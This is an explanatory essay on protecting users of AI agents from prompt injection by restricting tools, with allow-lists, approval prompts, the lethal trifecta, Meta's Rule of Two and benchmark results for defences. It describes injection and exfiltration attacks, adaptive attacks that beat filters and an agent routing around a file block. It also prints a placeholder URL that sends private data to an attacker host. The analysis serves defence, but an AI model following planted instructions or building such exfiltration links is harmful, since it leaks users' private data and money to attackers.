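# Restricting What AI Agents Can Do to Protect Users from Manipulation

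## What it means to take a capability away from an AI agent

An AI agent is a language model (a program that writes text by predicting what comes next) that can act through tools. It can open web pages, send messages, run code or buy things. It also reads a lot of material written by strangers, who can plant text there to steer it. An agent that follows the planted text may leak its user's private data, pass on a link to a fraudulent site or send money. One response is to filter the text. The other is to remove or narrow the capability that the attack needs. For example, an assistant that cannot load images cannot leak data by loading one. The user loses the capability too, so whether a restriction is justified depends on which attacks it stops and how much the user loses.

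### Agents and their tools

Anthropic's *Trustworthy agents in practice* defines an agent as a model that directs its own processes and tool use instead of following a fixed script. The model makes a plan, takes a step, looks at what happened and changes course if necessary, and it keeps going until it has finished or has a question for the user. In the company's example, Anthropic's model Claude files expenses from a business trip. It reads a photo of each receipt, picks out the amount and vendor, chooses a category and submits the claim in the employer's expense system. If the system flags a hotel bill for exceeding the nightly cap, Claude might ask whether to look up the expense policy before trying again.

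Tools are the services and applications the model can use, such as email, a calendar or that expense system. Without them, Claude could read the receipt but not file it. Even with tools, the model itself only produces text. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* documentation describes how this works for retrieving web pages. The model outputs a request containing an address, ordinary software fetches the page, and the page's text is returned to the model. Some software therefore always sits between the model's request and the resulting action, and that software can block the request.

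An affordance, or capability, is something a system makes it possible for an agent to do, such as display an image or start a payment. Removing it makes the action impossible whatever the model decides. OpenAI compares the agent to a customer-service worker who can give refunds. Some customers will lie to the worker, and some of the lies will work, so the employer uses software to limit how much the worker can refund. The limit holds even if the worker believes every lie.

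### Why a model cannot reliably tell who is giving the orders

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) defines prompt injection as instructions placed in external content to make a model do something its user did not ask for. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* classes it as social engineering, the security term for tricking people, but with a model as the target. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025), Simon Willison recalls naming it after SQL injection, an old attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command.

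Programmers prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the typed text to the database separately, so that the database never treats the text as a command. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 post for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that language models may never have an equivalent protection. Suppose a recruiter's system asks a model to score a CV, and the candidate has hidden a line in the CV asking for approval. The recruiter's request and the candidate's line reach the model as one run of tokens, the short pieces into which models divide text. The model only predicts the next token, and it has no mechanism for treating some tokens as commands and others as material.

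Labelling every email as data would not fix this, because the right label depends on the task. *Where Instruction Hierarchy Breaks* (Kariyappa and Suh, 2026) gives the example of an email asking when a company's next model will come out. An assistant asked to summarise new mail should just report the question, but one asked to write replies should treat it as a request to deal with, subject to the employer's rule against sharing project details with outsiders.

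Labels also affect models less than their designers intended. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, found that models attribute text to a speaker based more on how it sounds than on its label. Still, models' internal states can reflect whether a sentence is an instruction or mere material. *Readable Before Actionable* (2026) varied this distinction independently of formatting, then tried to read it from the model's internal states. The readout scored about 0.92 on a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect, while formatting cues alone scored 0.508.

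So the model can have at least some of the relevant information and still fail to act on it. Kariyappa and Suh found a similar failure when instructions conflicted without an attacker involved. They told Google's Gemma-4-31B-IT to answer only in English and later asked it for French. As the intervening conversation grew from one exchange to eight, the share of answers that kept to English fell from 61.7% to zero. Yet when they asked the same model only whether the two instructions conflicted, it answered correctly almost every time.

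Good models now resist most prompt-injection attacks, but not all. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports an attack success rate against Claude Opus 4.7 of roughly 0.1% for single attempts on a prompt-injection benchmark, and 5–6% after 100 adaptive attempts. Whether that is good enough depends on what the agent can do when an attack succeeds.

### Two ways to harm the user

One kind of harm occurs when the agent acts against its user. Microsoft (2025) divides this kind into data exfiltration, which means sending private data to someone who should not have it, and unintended actions, such as running an attacker's commands with the user's permissions.

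In the other kind of attack, the agent only answers, and the answer misleads the user. *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (Trail of Bits, 2026) describes attacks that made a browser agent state that Yuri Gagarin was the first man on the moon and recommend a company that does not exist. Such attacks work without moving any private data. Other examples would be a false warning about the user's bank account or a phishing link, which leads to a site posing as a trusted one in order to collect passwords. These attacks rely largely on the user's trust in the assistant. Microsoft describes a variant in which an agent with access to email sends phishing links to the user's colleagues. Because the messages come from the user's own account, they pass the standard checks for forged senders.

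A designer can stop an agent from leaking a file by closing its channels to the outside. Lying needs a different remedy, because it takes only the ability to write sentences, and an assistant without that ability is useless. Links fall between the two cases, since a link in an answer can take the user to a fake login page and can also carry the user's data away when clicked.

### How an address or an image carries data out

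A web address does more than name a place. When a browser or an agent opens one, it sends the site the whole address, and websites commonly keep a log of the addresses that visitors request. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) illustrates the danger with a placeholder:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`

The part of the URL up to the first single slash identifies the site to contact. Everything after it is sent with the request, including the field called "data" and its value, which follow the question mark. If an attacker tricks a model into filling in that value with a document title or an email address and then opening the URL, the attacker can read the information in the site's log, and the chat may show nothing unusual.

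An ordinary link can pass information about a user to a website. In a harmless example from OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links*, a user asks where to find cars to buy nearby, and ChatGPT offers a link to a car-search site with "London" in the address. Clicking the link reveals to the site where the user lives, which in this case is what the user wanted.

An image can make a browser send private data without a click. Web pages usually contain the addresses of their images, and Kansas State University's *The DOM and External Resource Loading* explains that the browser requests each image as it works through the page. Chat assistants that run in a browser load images the same way, so if an agent's answer includes an image whose address contains private data, displaying the answer sends the data. Researchers have demonstrated this against commercial products. A text link with the same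 address sends nothing until the user clicks it, unless the application fetches the link itself. Some applications fetch a preview of every link they show, and OpenAI counts link previews with embedded images among the requests that can happen in the background.

### Sources, sinks and the lethal trifecta

Security engineers were using the terms "source" and "sink" before AI agents existed. A source is a way for an attacker to influence the system, and a sink is a capability that becomes dangerous once the attacker has that influence. Lecture slides from UT Austin list emails, web pages and pull requests (proposed changes to a program's code) as sources for an agent. The sinks they list are the command line, the network and any cloud service that can change or disclose something. An attack needs both a source and a sink. An injected instruction that reaches no sink may still spoil the agent's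 answer, but it cannot move data or money.

Willison's "lethal trifecta" applies the same idea to data theft. The trifecta combines exposure to untrusted content (the source), the ability to communicate externally (the sink), and access to private data (the target). An attacker can trick an agent that has all three into fetching the data and sending it out. The trifecta does not cover every risk, since an agent that can make payments can lose its user's money without reading any private documents.

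In June 2026, Willison wrote that the only way to solve the trifecta is to cut one of its three legs, and that outward communication is by far the easiest to restrict without making the system much less useful. An email assistant, for example, is pointless if it cannot read the inbox, and most inboxes are full of messages from outsiders. David C reports a stricter rule from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. Nobody would give a random correspondent access to privileged tools, so a model reading that correspondent's email should not have access to them either.

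Some recent evidence points the other way. In August 2026 Anthropic published a commissioned test of Claude Code, its programming agent, in a mode where an automated check replaces most requests for the user's approval. None of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three recent Claude models, and an Anthropic employee suggested that the post should have been called "defeating the lethal trifecta". Willison would like to believe it but wants more independent confirmation, and he doubts that such a check could catch a malicious software package that the agent seems to have a good reason to install. The 720 attempts came from 72 prepared scenarios, so the result is encouraging for those scenarios but weaker evidence about new kinds of attack.

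### Grades of restriction on one email assistant

An assistant that summarises the morning's email reads the whole inbox, and strangers can write to that inbox. Its summary appears in a window that can show images and links, and it can open web pages mentioned in a message or send a reply. The assistant therefore has all three parts of the trifecta. A designer worried about a hostile message has roughly six options, ranging from those that take away the most capability to those that take away the least.

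| Grade | What the email assistant can still do | Who decides |
|---|---|---|
| Full removal | Write a plain-text summary; no images, no web pages, no sending | Software |
| Allow-list | Load images and pages from listed sites only | Software, using a list that a person wrote |
| Known-URL rule | Open only addresses it did not compose itself | Software, using a record of where addresses came from |
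| Approval prompt | Open a page or send a reply once the user agrees | The user, case by case |
| Warning | Everything, under a notice about the risk | The user |
| Content filter | Everything, with text that has passed a check | A model |

When software decides, the control is deterministic, so the same request always gets the same result, however persuasive the email was. Microsoft prefers such controls where possible because they can guarantee that a particular attack fails, though the guarantee doesn't extend to other attacks. The simplest case is removing a capability entirely, and an optional ChatGPT setting goes a long way towards this. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes how the setting limits browsing to stored copies of pages, so that no live request leaves the company's own network. OpenAI's help page for the setting, *Lockdown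 Mode*, states that a hostile instruction in an uploaded file can still produce a wrong answer. Similarly, our email assistant could no longer leak the inbox through an image, but it could still tell the user that a fraudulent invoice was genuine.

An allow-list restores some of the usefulness. The assistant might show images only from the employer's own site, for example. But a list of sites gives little information about what those sites can do. Many reputable sites forward visitors to other addresses, as OpenAI points out, so a request can start at a trusted site and finish at an attacker's. Anthropic came to regard its own allow-list as a grant of capability, since whoever is steering the agent can use every function available at a listed site.

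The known-URL rule checks the exact address rather than the site. To steal the contents of the inbox, an attacker needs the agent to build an address containing them, which the rule forbids. Anthropic's tool fetches an address if, for example, the user supplied it or a search returned it. The company warns that some risk remains and suggests using an allow-list or turning the tool off where leaks are a concern. OpenAI instead checks whether an independent crawler, with no access to anyone's conversations, has already seen that exact address on the public web. Email is a hard case for OpenAI's version, probably because so many links in email are unique to the recipient.

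An address that only one person has ever received will not be in a public index, so the software has to refuse it or ask the user.

An approval prompt holds an action until the user answers. Anthropic lets users set each of Claude's actions to "always allow", "needs approval" or "block", so the email assistant could read the calendar freely but have to ask before inviting anyone to a meeting. In Microsoft's Outlook, Copilot drafts a message, but the user has to approve it and press send. ChatGPT sometimes shows the user the information that a request would transmit. These checks depend on the user's attention, and Anthropic observes that people sometimes tune out repeated prompts.

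A warning takes less of the user's attention but also provides less protection. OpenAI puts an "Elevated Risk" label on certain features, including the setting that gives its coding agent access to the internet. The user reads the label when switching the feature on, which may be weeks before any hostile text arrives, and the label does not restrict the agent after that. Products often mix the two grades. ChatGPT's dialog for an unverified link, for example, contains a warning, but the link also stays closed until the user chooses to open it.

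A content filter leaves every capability in place and is meant to catch the hostile email on its way in. Microsoft's Prompt Shields is a classifier, a model that sorts text into categories, which the company trained on known injection techniques. Its verdicts are probabilistic, so some attacks will get past it. OpenAI objects that a well-written injection looks like ordinary correspondence, and that recognising one amounts to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. This weakness is serious when the attacker wants to steal data, because a designer could instead close the channel the data would leave through. There is no such channel to close when the attacker wants to put a false sentence in the summary, so a filter is one of the few defences left, even though it misses some attacks.

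## The argument for removing capabilities instead of filtering text

The case for restricting an agent's actions, instead of filtering what it reads, is an argument about design. It has four steps:

1. An attacker can rephrase an attack as often as they like.
2. A filter has to recognise deception, often without the context it would need.
3. An agent has only a few possible actions, and its designer can list them.
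4. Software can therefore limit those actions, and the limits hold even after an attacker has fooled the model.

Experiments mostly support the argument's claims about attackers and filters. The claim that designers can list an agent's actions is less well supported, and several restrictions have failed because the list was incomplete.

### The customer-service worker

OpenAI's March 2026 version of the argument begins with how attacks have changed. Early on, someone could edit a Wikipedia article to include instructions for AI agents, and models would often follow them. As models got better at ignoring such instructions, attackers began using the methods of con artists. In 2025, outside researchers reported an attack email to OpenAI that read like routine correspondence about a company restructuring. It worked half the time in tests where the user had asked ChatGPT to research the day's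 email.

OpenAI therefore compares an agent to a customer-service worker whose employer uses software that limits refunds and can flag likely phishing emails. It recommends asking what controls would apply to a person in the agent's position and applying the same ones to the agent.

If anything, agents are easier to deceive than human support workers. A worker who hears the same odd story ten times in a morning will probably get suspicious, but an agent that starts each conversation afresh won't notice the repetition. A fraudster can also often practise on the same model beforehand, which isn't possible with a human worker.

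### Attackers who learn from failure

Many defences look good against a fixed list of attacks. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 published defences with adaptive attacks, which use the result of each attempt to revise the next. Some of the defences were meant for prompt injection and others for jailbreaks, in which users themselves try to get round a model's rules. Most had reported attack success rates near zero, but the adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12. One of them, Spotlighting, uses markers to show the model which text to trust. Fixed attacks on it succeeded as little as 1% of the time, and adaptive attacks more than 95%.

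On a selected set of scenarios, participants in a competition with over 500 entrants collectively succeeded every time, compared with 69% of the time for automated search.

Nasr and colleagues put no tight limit on computing power, and their attack software received a detector's confidence score after each attempt. Someone who sends a hostile email normally gets no such feedback, so 90% is closer to a worst case than to a forecast. But an attacker who can run the same filter privately can get the same feedback.

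### What a filter has to recognise

The 12 defences included four detectors, which classify text as safe or unsafe. Automated attacks got past three of them more than 90% of the time and past the fourth, PIGuard, 71% of the time. Many of the successful texts did not look harmful. A message might mention a company policy that requires some extra step, and a detector cannot check whether the company has that policy. Making the detector stricter would block more honest messages. Nasr and colleagues still recommend detectors as one part of a defence, because they are easy to install and stop some unsophisticated attacks.

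A better filter might stop more attacks. *Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter* (2025) presents a language model meant to separate injected instructions from clean data. Attacks designed specifically to fool it succeeded less than 1% of the time. However, the researchers wrote several such attacks in advance and picked one at random for each test case, which is an easier test than an attacker who can revise after each failure.

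Some filters don't have to recognise deception. Ordinary code, for example, can look for a known password without judging whether anyone is lying. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) tested nine defences with more than 20,000 attacks from a system that adapted over hundreds of rounds. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually broke. The only one that held used ordinary code to check the model's answers before they reached the user, and it had no leaks in 15,000 attacks.

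The argument holds for filters on incoming text, but not for all filters. Outgoing text is easier to check when the designer knows exactly what must not be sent. The contents of an inbox are harder to protect this way, because almost any of them might be private and an attacker can ask the model to reword them.

### One hundred attempts at a 99% filter

Suppose a filter has a 99% chance of stopping each attack, independent of the others. The chance that at least one of 100 attacks gets through is 1 − 0.99^100, or about 63%. With 300 attacks, it is about 95%. To reduce that 95% to 5%, the filter would have to stop about 99.98% of attacks.

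The calculation counts passing the filter as success, although the model might still refuse. It also assumes that attempts are independent and equally likely to work, which is not true of real attempts. Anthropic reports a success rate of roughly 0.1% per attempt for Claude Opus 4.7. At that rate, at least one of 100 independent attempts would succeed about 9.5% of the time, but Anthropic's figure for 100 adaptive attempts is 5–6%. This may be because a model that resists one attack in a given situation tends to resist the next one too.

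A newer experiment deviates in the opposite direction. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, Kurakin, Karande and colleagues (2026) had a group of AI agents look for texts that would make a target model use a tool unrelated to its task. The agents shared notes and had up to 320 attempts in each of 100 invented scenarios. With Google's Gemini 4 Argon as both attacker and target, the attack succeeded in 13% of scenarios within 150 attempts and in 34% within 320. If the chance of success per attempt had stayed constant, the 13% would have risen to only about 26%. The attackers seem to have been learning, although with only 100 scenarios, some of the difference between 26% and 34% could be luck.

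The 63% therefore illustrates how small chances add up, and the true figure could be higher or lower. An attacker can also spread attempts across many people. If 300 people each receive one hostile email and the filter stops 99%, about three get through.

### Victorian iron and failing grades

People who accept this arithmetic still disagree about the remedy. In September 2025 the Economist argued that AI engineers should think like the builders of Victorian England, who overbuilt because they could not trust their iron, adding redundancy in case a part failed. Willison, in *How to stop AI's "lethal trifecta"*, quotes the passage and mostly agrees that software built on language models needs tolerances and redundancy. But he rejects the approach for security, where "99% is a failing grade", because an attacker will look for the other 1%.

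Redundancy works when parts fail independently. If two filters each stopped 99% of attacks and their mistakes were unrelated, only one attack in 10,000 would pass both, and the chance of at least one success in 300 attempts would drop from 95% to about 3%. But Nasr and colleagues found that their attacks still worked against several detectors combined. *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) argues for combining detectors that use different kinds of signal, since an attacker would have to evade all of them at once. This seems plausible, especially for signals that are hard to fake, such as where a text came from.

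Willison seems right about a determined attacker with many tries. Still, overbuilding can mean limiting what the agent can pay out instead of adding filters. That limit is a safety margin that does not depend on the model or the filter being right.

### What a refund cap guarantees

Suppose a shop lets its agent pay at most 20 refunds a day, of up to $50 each. The shop can then lose at most $1,000 a day to fraudulent refunds, however many people write in and however convincing their stories are.

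This calculation has assumptions too. The payment system has to enforce both limits, since a model could be persuaded to ignore them. One count has to cover every copy of the agent, because ten copies with separate counts could lose $10,000 a day. The agent must have no other way to give money away, such as gift cards. If these assumptions hold, the $1,000 daily bound can be calculated without estimating how often the model is deceived, though losses could reach $365,000 over a year if nobody notices.

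The cap limits the worst loss, but a filter would still be worth having because it lowers the usual one. If 100 fraudulent requests arrive each day and the filter stops 99% of them, the shop loses about $50 on an average day.

An argument from design can show that a larger loss is impossible if the software works as described. The shop would have to test the software to find out whether it does. The argument also can't show whether the cap is worth the delay it causes for a customer who is owed $80 or one who asks for the day's twenty-first refund. To decide that, the shop would need to know how many such customers it has and how long they would wait for a person to help.

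A cap leaves the injection in place, which is a common objection to it, and the agent can still do harm within its limits. It could pay 20 fraudsters early in the day and have nothing left for honest customers. It could also give customers false information, which a refund limit doesn't prevent. The usual reply, that a bounded loss is better than an unbounded one, is convincing for money and stolen data but doesn't help much when a user believes a false answer.

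A limit on amounts also doesn't ensure that the company wanted a payment. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) describes an invoice agent that notices a document-signing subscription is about to lapse and tries to renew it. The company may allow both the vendor and the amount, but renewing means signing a contract, which nobody asked the agent to do. OpenAI proposes limiting the agent to its assigned task and requiring separate approval for any new commitment.

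### Can a designer list the actions?

Listing everything an agent can do is hard, even for an email assistant with only five tools, because a tool often does more than its name suggests and two tools may do the same thing. Google's coding product Antigravity blocked its agent from opening certain private files with its file-reading tools, but still let it run commands, which could also read those files. In a demonstration by the security company PromptArmor, which Willison recounted in November 2025, the agent found this workaround by itself while following an attacker's instructions. A capable model under an attacker's influence will look for such gaps. Google listed data theft through the product's browser agent as a known issue that it was working to fix.

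Designers sometimes allow a dangerous action even when it is on the list. In June 2026 Willison reported that people had taken over high-profile Instagram accounts by asking Meta's support bot to link a new email address to them. This case supports removing capabilities, because a filter might well have passed such a short, polite request, but the takeovers needed a bot that could change the address on its own.

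Harmless actions can also combine into a harmful one. Kurakin and colleagues repeat an example in which someone lists the files in a folder, encrypts them and deletes the originals. Each step is routine administration, but together they amount to a ransomware attack. OpenAI's guide therefore advises companies to review capabilities in combination as well as alone. An agent that can read sensitive data can leak it if it can also send messages, and one with a command line and unrestricted network access can get around other controls.

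The number of combinations grows quickly. Ten tools form 45 pairs and fifty form 1,225, before counting longer sequences. The list also goes out of date, since an update may let a read-only connection write. The best answer is probably OpenAI's advice to place each control as close as possible to the effect it limits. A designer who blocks the agent's network access doesn't have to examine every combination of tools that would have used it.

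Even then, an attacker may get around the restriction through another system. The makers of Cline, a coding tool, used an agent to sort incoming bug reports and kept their publishing credentials away from it. But the agent could run commands, and it shared a cache with the process that built new releases, which did have the credentials. The researcher Adnan Khan reported the weakness, but the company was slow to act, and an attacker published an unauthorised version of Cline, which the company has since retracted. Restricting the agent would have been enough only if the designer had included the shared cache among the things the agent could affect.

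### Meta's Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the argument into a rule for designers. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have at most two of these properties in any one session:

- **A:** it processes untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change state or communicate externally.

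Changing state means altering something outside the conversation, such as deleting a file or making a booking. A new session starts with an empty context, so text from the old one is gone. An agent that needs all three properties in one session should act only under supervision, for example by a person who approves its actions.

The rule resembles Willison's lethal trifecta but also covers harms other than data theft, such as an agent deleting its user's files. In *New prompt injection papers*, Willison (2025) welcomed the rule for this reason and called it the best practical advice available in the absence of reliable defences.

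Meta applies the rule to an imaginary Email-Bot that receives a spam message containing instructions to forward the user's inbox. The designer could let the bot read mail only from trusted senders, keep it away from private data, or let it send mail only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft. An email assistant without access to private email would be of little use, and one that ignores mail from strangers would miss a lot. Restricting what it sends would leave it more useful than either of the other options.

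The objection that useful agents need all three properties is partly right, but Meta's examples show that narrowing one is often enough. A travel assistant can search the web and know the user's personal details, as long as it asks before booking and does not open URLs it has written itself. A research assistant can browse the web in a browser that isn't logged in to anything. An agent can also change its properties partway through a session, for example by giving up outside communication before it accesses internal systems.

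But Meta concedes that some uses people want will not fit these restrictions, such as a process that runs in the background, where stopping for approval is disruptive or ineffective. Some researchers have designed agents with formal guarantees for tasks that need both private data and untrusted text. Without such a design, someone has to give up part of the task or accept the risk. OpenAI adds that controls that interfere with legitimate work can push employees towards tools with weaker controls, which may leave the company worse off.

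Willison soon pointed out in an online discussion that an agent with untrusted input and the power to change state can do harm even without private data. Meta's diagram of the rule had marked that combination as "safe". But an agent that fills in web forms, for example, could be made to send spam. Willison acknowledged that making an exception for this combination would make the rule less simple. Meta describes the rule as a supplement to ordinary security principles and says it is not meant to prevent false statements in an agent's answers.

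### If models become harder to fool

Restrictions would be less valuable if injections stopped working, and models have become much more resistant to them. Fernando Irarrázaval challenged the public to extract a secret from an email assistant running on Claude Opus 4.6. About 2,000 people made 6,000 attempts, and none succeeded. Kurakin and colleagues report that attacks from a large public competition now succeed less than 1% of the time against recent Gemini models and some versions of Claude.

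Their own experiment is less encouraging, because the attackers had improved as well. Weaker models succeeded against Gemini 4 Argon in at most about 3% of scenarios within 150 attempts, compared with 13% when it attacked itself. The strongest attacker succeeded against three open-weight models, which anyone can download and run, in 99% of scenarios over the full 320 attempts. In some respects, these figures overstate the danger to a real user. The researchers switched off the protections outside the Gemini models and tried to trigger only harmless tool uses, so a model may have done things it would have refused to do if they had looked dangerous.

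OpenAI expects that a maximally intelligent model will resist social engineering better than a person, but adds that using one will not always be feasible or affordable. Some attacks also do not depend on the model following the attacker's instructions. In August 2026, weeks after Anthropic published its test in which none of 720 injection attempts succeeded, the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported an attack on the same automatic mode of Claude Code that worked 80% of the time. Willison came to agree that it was not a classic prompt injection, since Claude never followed instructions from the hostile website. Claude ran ordinary-looking code without detecting that it would load a file the attacker had supplied. Rehberger recommends running agents in an isolated environment with restricted network access and no credentials within reach, which limits the damage whether or not the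 model detects the attack.

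## Benchmark tests of agents with restricted tools

To test a restriction, researchers give an agent ordinary tasks and plant hostile instructions in some of the material it has to read. They then measure the attack success rate, which is the share of attacks that achieve the attacker's aim, and utility, which is the share of ordinary tasks the agent completes with the restriction in place. An agent with no tools would score close to zero on both, so neither score alone is enough to judge a restriction.

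In these tests, restricting an agent's tools usually cuts attack success a lot, sometimes to zero. The loss of utility varies much more, with some restricted agents completing nearly as many tasks as before and others almost none.

### How AgentDojo works

Many of the later tests build on *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), which simulates an office suite, a bank, a travel agency and the workplace chat service Slack. It has 97 user tasks across these four environments and a set of attacker goals for each environment. Each user task is paired with each attacker goal in the same environment, so the office suite's 40 tasks and 6 attacker goals make 240 pairs. The four environments together have 629 pairs.

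In one banking task, the user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file, which may also contain an instruction to send money to an attacker's account. When the agent has finished, ordinary code checks the simulated bank to see whether the bill was paid and whether the attacker received any money. Debenedetti and colleagues did not use a language model as the judge, because an injected instruction that fools the agent might fool the judge too.

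In one benchmark, OpenAI's GPT-4o completed 69% of tasks without an attack and 50% under attack. The attacks succeeded in 48% of cases.

Those figures are out of date. *aiAuthZ* (2026) ran the same style of attack on two current models in 20 banking cases, and it never succeeded when the models had no defence. But that attack is a single fixed text that has been public since 2024. Stronger attacks still work on current models, so a restriction can make a large difference.

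### The tool filter

AgentDojo came with a simple restriction called the tool filter. Before the agent reads any outside data, the model lists the tools that the user's request will need, and the agent works with only those. If the user asks for a summary of recent emails, the agent can read email but not send it, so it cannot carry out an injected instruction to forward the inbox.

The filter cut the success rate of attacks against GPT-4o from about 50% to 7.5%. It worked well because many user tasks only require reading, while most attacks require the agent to change or send something.

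However, the filter fails in the 17% of AgentDojo's cases where the tools needed for the task are also enough for the attack. For example, an agent that pays bills has to keep its payment tool, which is also the tool an attacker needs to get a payment. The filter also fails when the agent can't tell in advance which tools it will need. And if a user gives the agent several tasks in one session, a later task may bring back a dangerous tool while the planted text is still in the agent's context.

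Later tests of the filter gave mixed results. In *Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents*, Alizadeh, Samei and colleagues (2025) tried to make a banking agent email its user's personal details to an attacker. With the filter on, the attacks succeeded 3.1% of the time on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks and almost never on a larger set of 48, though the filter also reduced the agent's utility. The filter did much worse in *PACE*, where Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) tested it on a different benchmark, MSB. There, it reduced attack success against OpenAI's gpt-5.6-luna only from 99% to 53%.

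### One email task under several design patterns

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) proposes the stricter principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, it should be impossible for that text to trigger any consequential action. The paper describes six ways to build agents that follow this principle and applies them to ten case studies. Agents built in these ways cannot do arbitrary tasks.

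One of their examples is an assistant whose user asks it to send today's schedule to a boss, John Doe. Suppose a stranger has sent the user a calendar invitation with a planted instruction in it. Under the pattern called plan-then-execute, the assistant works like this:

1. The model reads only the user's request and writes a plan: read today's calendar, then email the result to John's address.
2. Software carries out the first step, and the planted instruction reaches the model along with the rest of the calendar.
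3. The model writes the message, and software sends it to the address in the plan.

The planted instruction can't add a step or change the recipient, because the model settled both before reading it. But it can still change what the message says, so the stranger could send John a false claim or a phishing link from the user's own account.

Other tasks give an attacker more opportunity. If the user asks the assistant to answer the stranger's email, the stranger is the intended recipient, and the planted text could get the assistant to include private information in the reply.

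The dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023, uses two models. One plans and has the tools but never sees untrusted text, while the other reads the calendar and has no tools. Software stores the second model's output under a label, and the planning model can use the label to have the text emailed without seeing it. The code-then-execute pattern extends this by having the planning model write a short program. For John's schedule, three lines of code read the calendar, have the other model format it, and send the result to John. With either pattern, the stranger could still corrupt the message.

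The remaining patterns are narrower:

- **Action selector:** the model picks from a fixed menu of actions and never sees their results.
- **Map-reduce:** a separate model reads each document and may return only a restricted answer, such as whether a file is an invoice. A hostile file can then do little more than get itself misfiled.
- **Context minimisation:** the system deletes the user's own words once the model has turned them into, say, a database query. This helps when a user has pasted in hostile text without noticing.

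Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think a fixed plan would make an email assistant only slightly less useful, because its choice of actions should rarely depend on what strangers write. There are obvious exceptions, such as when a user asks the agent to do everything on a to-do list emailed by a colleague.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) sorts AgentDojo's tasks by whether the agent has to look at the data to know what to do next, which gives a way to check how common the exceptions are. The agent had to look at the data in 5% of the office tasks, 10% of the travel tasks, 44% of the banking tasks and 43% of the Slack tasks, or about 20 of the 97 tasks overall. So Beurer-Kellner and colleagues seem to be right about AgentDojo's office tasks, but their argument doesn't carry over to banking or workplace chat.

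### CaMeL and the cost of a fixed plan

CaMeL, a 2025 design from a team that included two of AgentDojo's creators, implements the code-then-execute pattern. A planning model writes a program from the user's request alone, and a second model, which has no tools, processes the untrusted text. The software that runs the program tracks where each piece of data came from and can use that record to decide whether to allow a step. For example, it could block an attempt to send the schedule to an address that came from a stranger's invitation.

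Li and colleagues tested CaMeL on three 2026 models and reported the success rate of whichever group of attacks worked best. On AgentDojo, CaMeL cut attack success against Alibaba's Qwen-3.8-27B from 48% to 0.3%, but utility fell from 63% to 35%. With gpt-5.6-luna, attack success fell from 100% to 36% and utility from 74% to 57%.

The 36% is surprising for a design that fixes its plan in advance. Some of these attacks may have changed the content of a planned action, as in the message to John. The re-run may also have used settings that CaMeL's designers would not have chosen.

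CaMeL did far worse on open-ended work. *AgentDyn* (2026) is a benchmark of 60 tasks and 560 attack cases in which the agent has to plan as it goes and follow helpful instructions written by third parties. The tasks average 7.1 steps and involve about three applications each. In Li and colleagues' tests, undefended agents completed 63–75% of these tasks. With CaMeL, two of the three models completed none and the third completed 3.75%. No attacks succeeded against the first two models, but this is not much of a security success because they also completed no tasks.

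This is to be expected when an agent writes its plan before reading the instructions it needs. *AgentDyn* also found large losses with the tool filter, but content filters did no better. Two of them, ProtectAI and PIGuard, failed to distinguish helpful instructions from malicious ones and reduced utility to nearly zero. Open-ended tasks are therefore a problem for both approaches, so they are not a reason to prefer content filters.

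### Checking each action when it comes up

A designer can let the agent plan freely and have software check each action before it happens, instead of fixing the whole plan in advance. Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built FIDES, which labels every piece of data by whether it is trusted and who may see it. If untrusted text has entered the planning model's context, the software blocks consequential actions such as payments. To avoid blocking actions too often, FIDES stores untrusted text outside the planning model's context, much as the dual LLM pattern does.

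Sometimes the agent needs information from the hidden text. Suppose the user wants it to create a calendar event if any of three emails contains a meeting request. A second model can read the emails and return only a yes or no, which is too short to contain an instruction. Costa and colleagues left this restriction on answers out of the version of FIDES they tested on AgentDojo, because most of the tasks did not need it.

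In their test, 152 attacks succeeded against GPT-4o without a defence. The tool filter reduced this to 20, and FIDES with its checks switched on reduced it to zero, but utility averaged over the four environments fell from 84% to 50%. Costa and colleagues emphasise a more favourable comparison: FIDES completes 8 percentage points more tasks than a basic agent. But that agent was subject to the same kind of security checks, which had already cut its utility to 42%.

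Many of the failures were by design. AgentDojo's banking tasks often ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which FIDES is meant to prevent when the file is untrusted.

*Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) controls the details of each action as well as the choice of tool. A rule might let the agent send Slack messages, but only to the user. A language model writes the first set of rules from the user's request and proposes changes as the agent learns more. Ordinary software then checks whether each change would allow anything new. A person must approve any change that would, while changes that only tighten the rules take effect automatically.

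Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0% with GPT-4o and left utility about the same. Shi and colleagues had the system approve every request for new permissions, to imitate a careless user, so the low rate did not depend on good human judgement. On ASB, another benchmark, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%, and most of the attacks that still worked used tools with names and descriptions very similar to those of legitimate tools.

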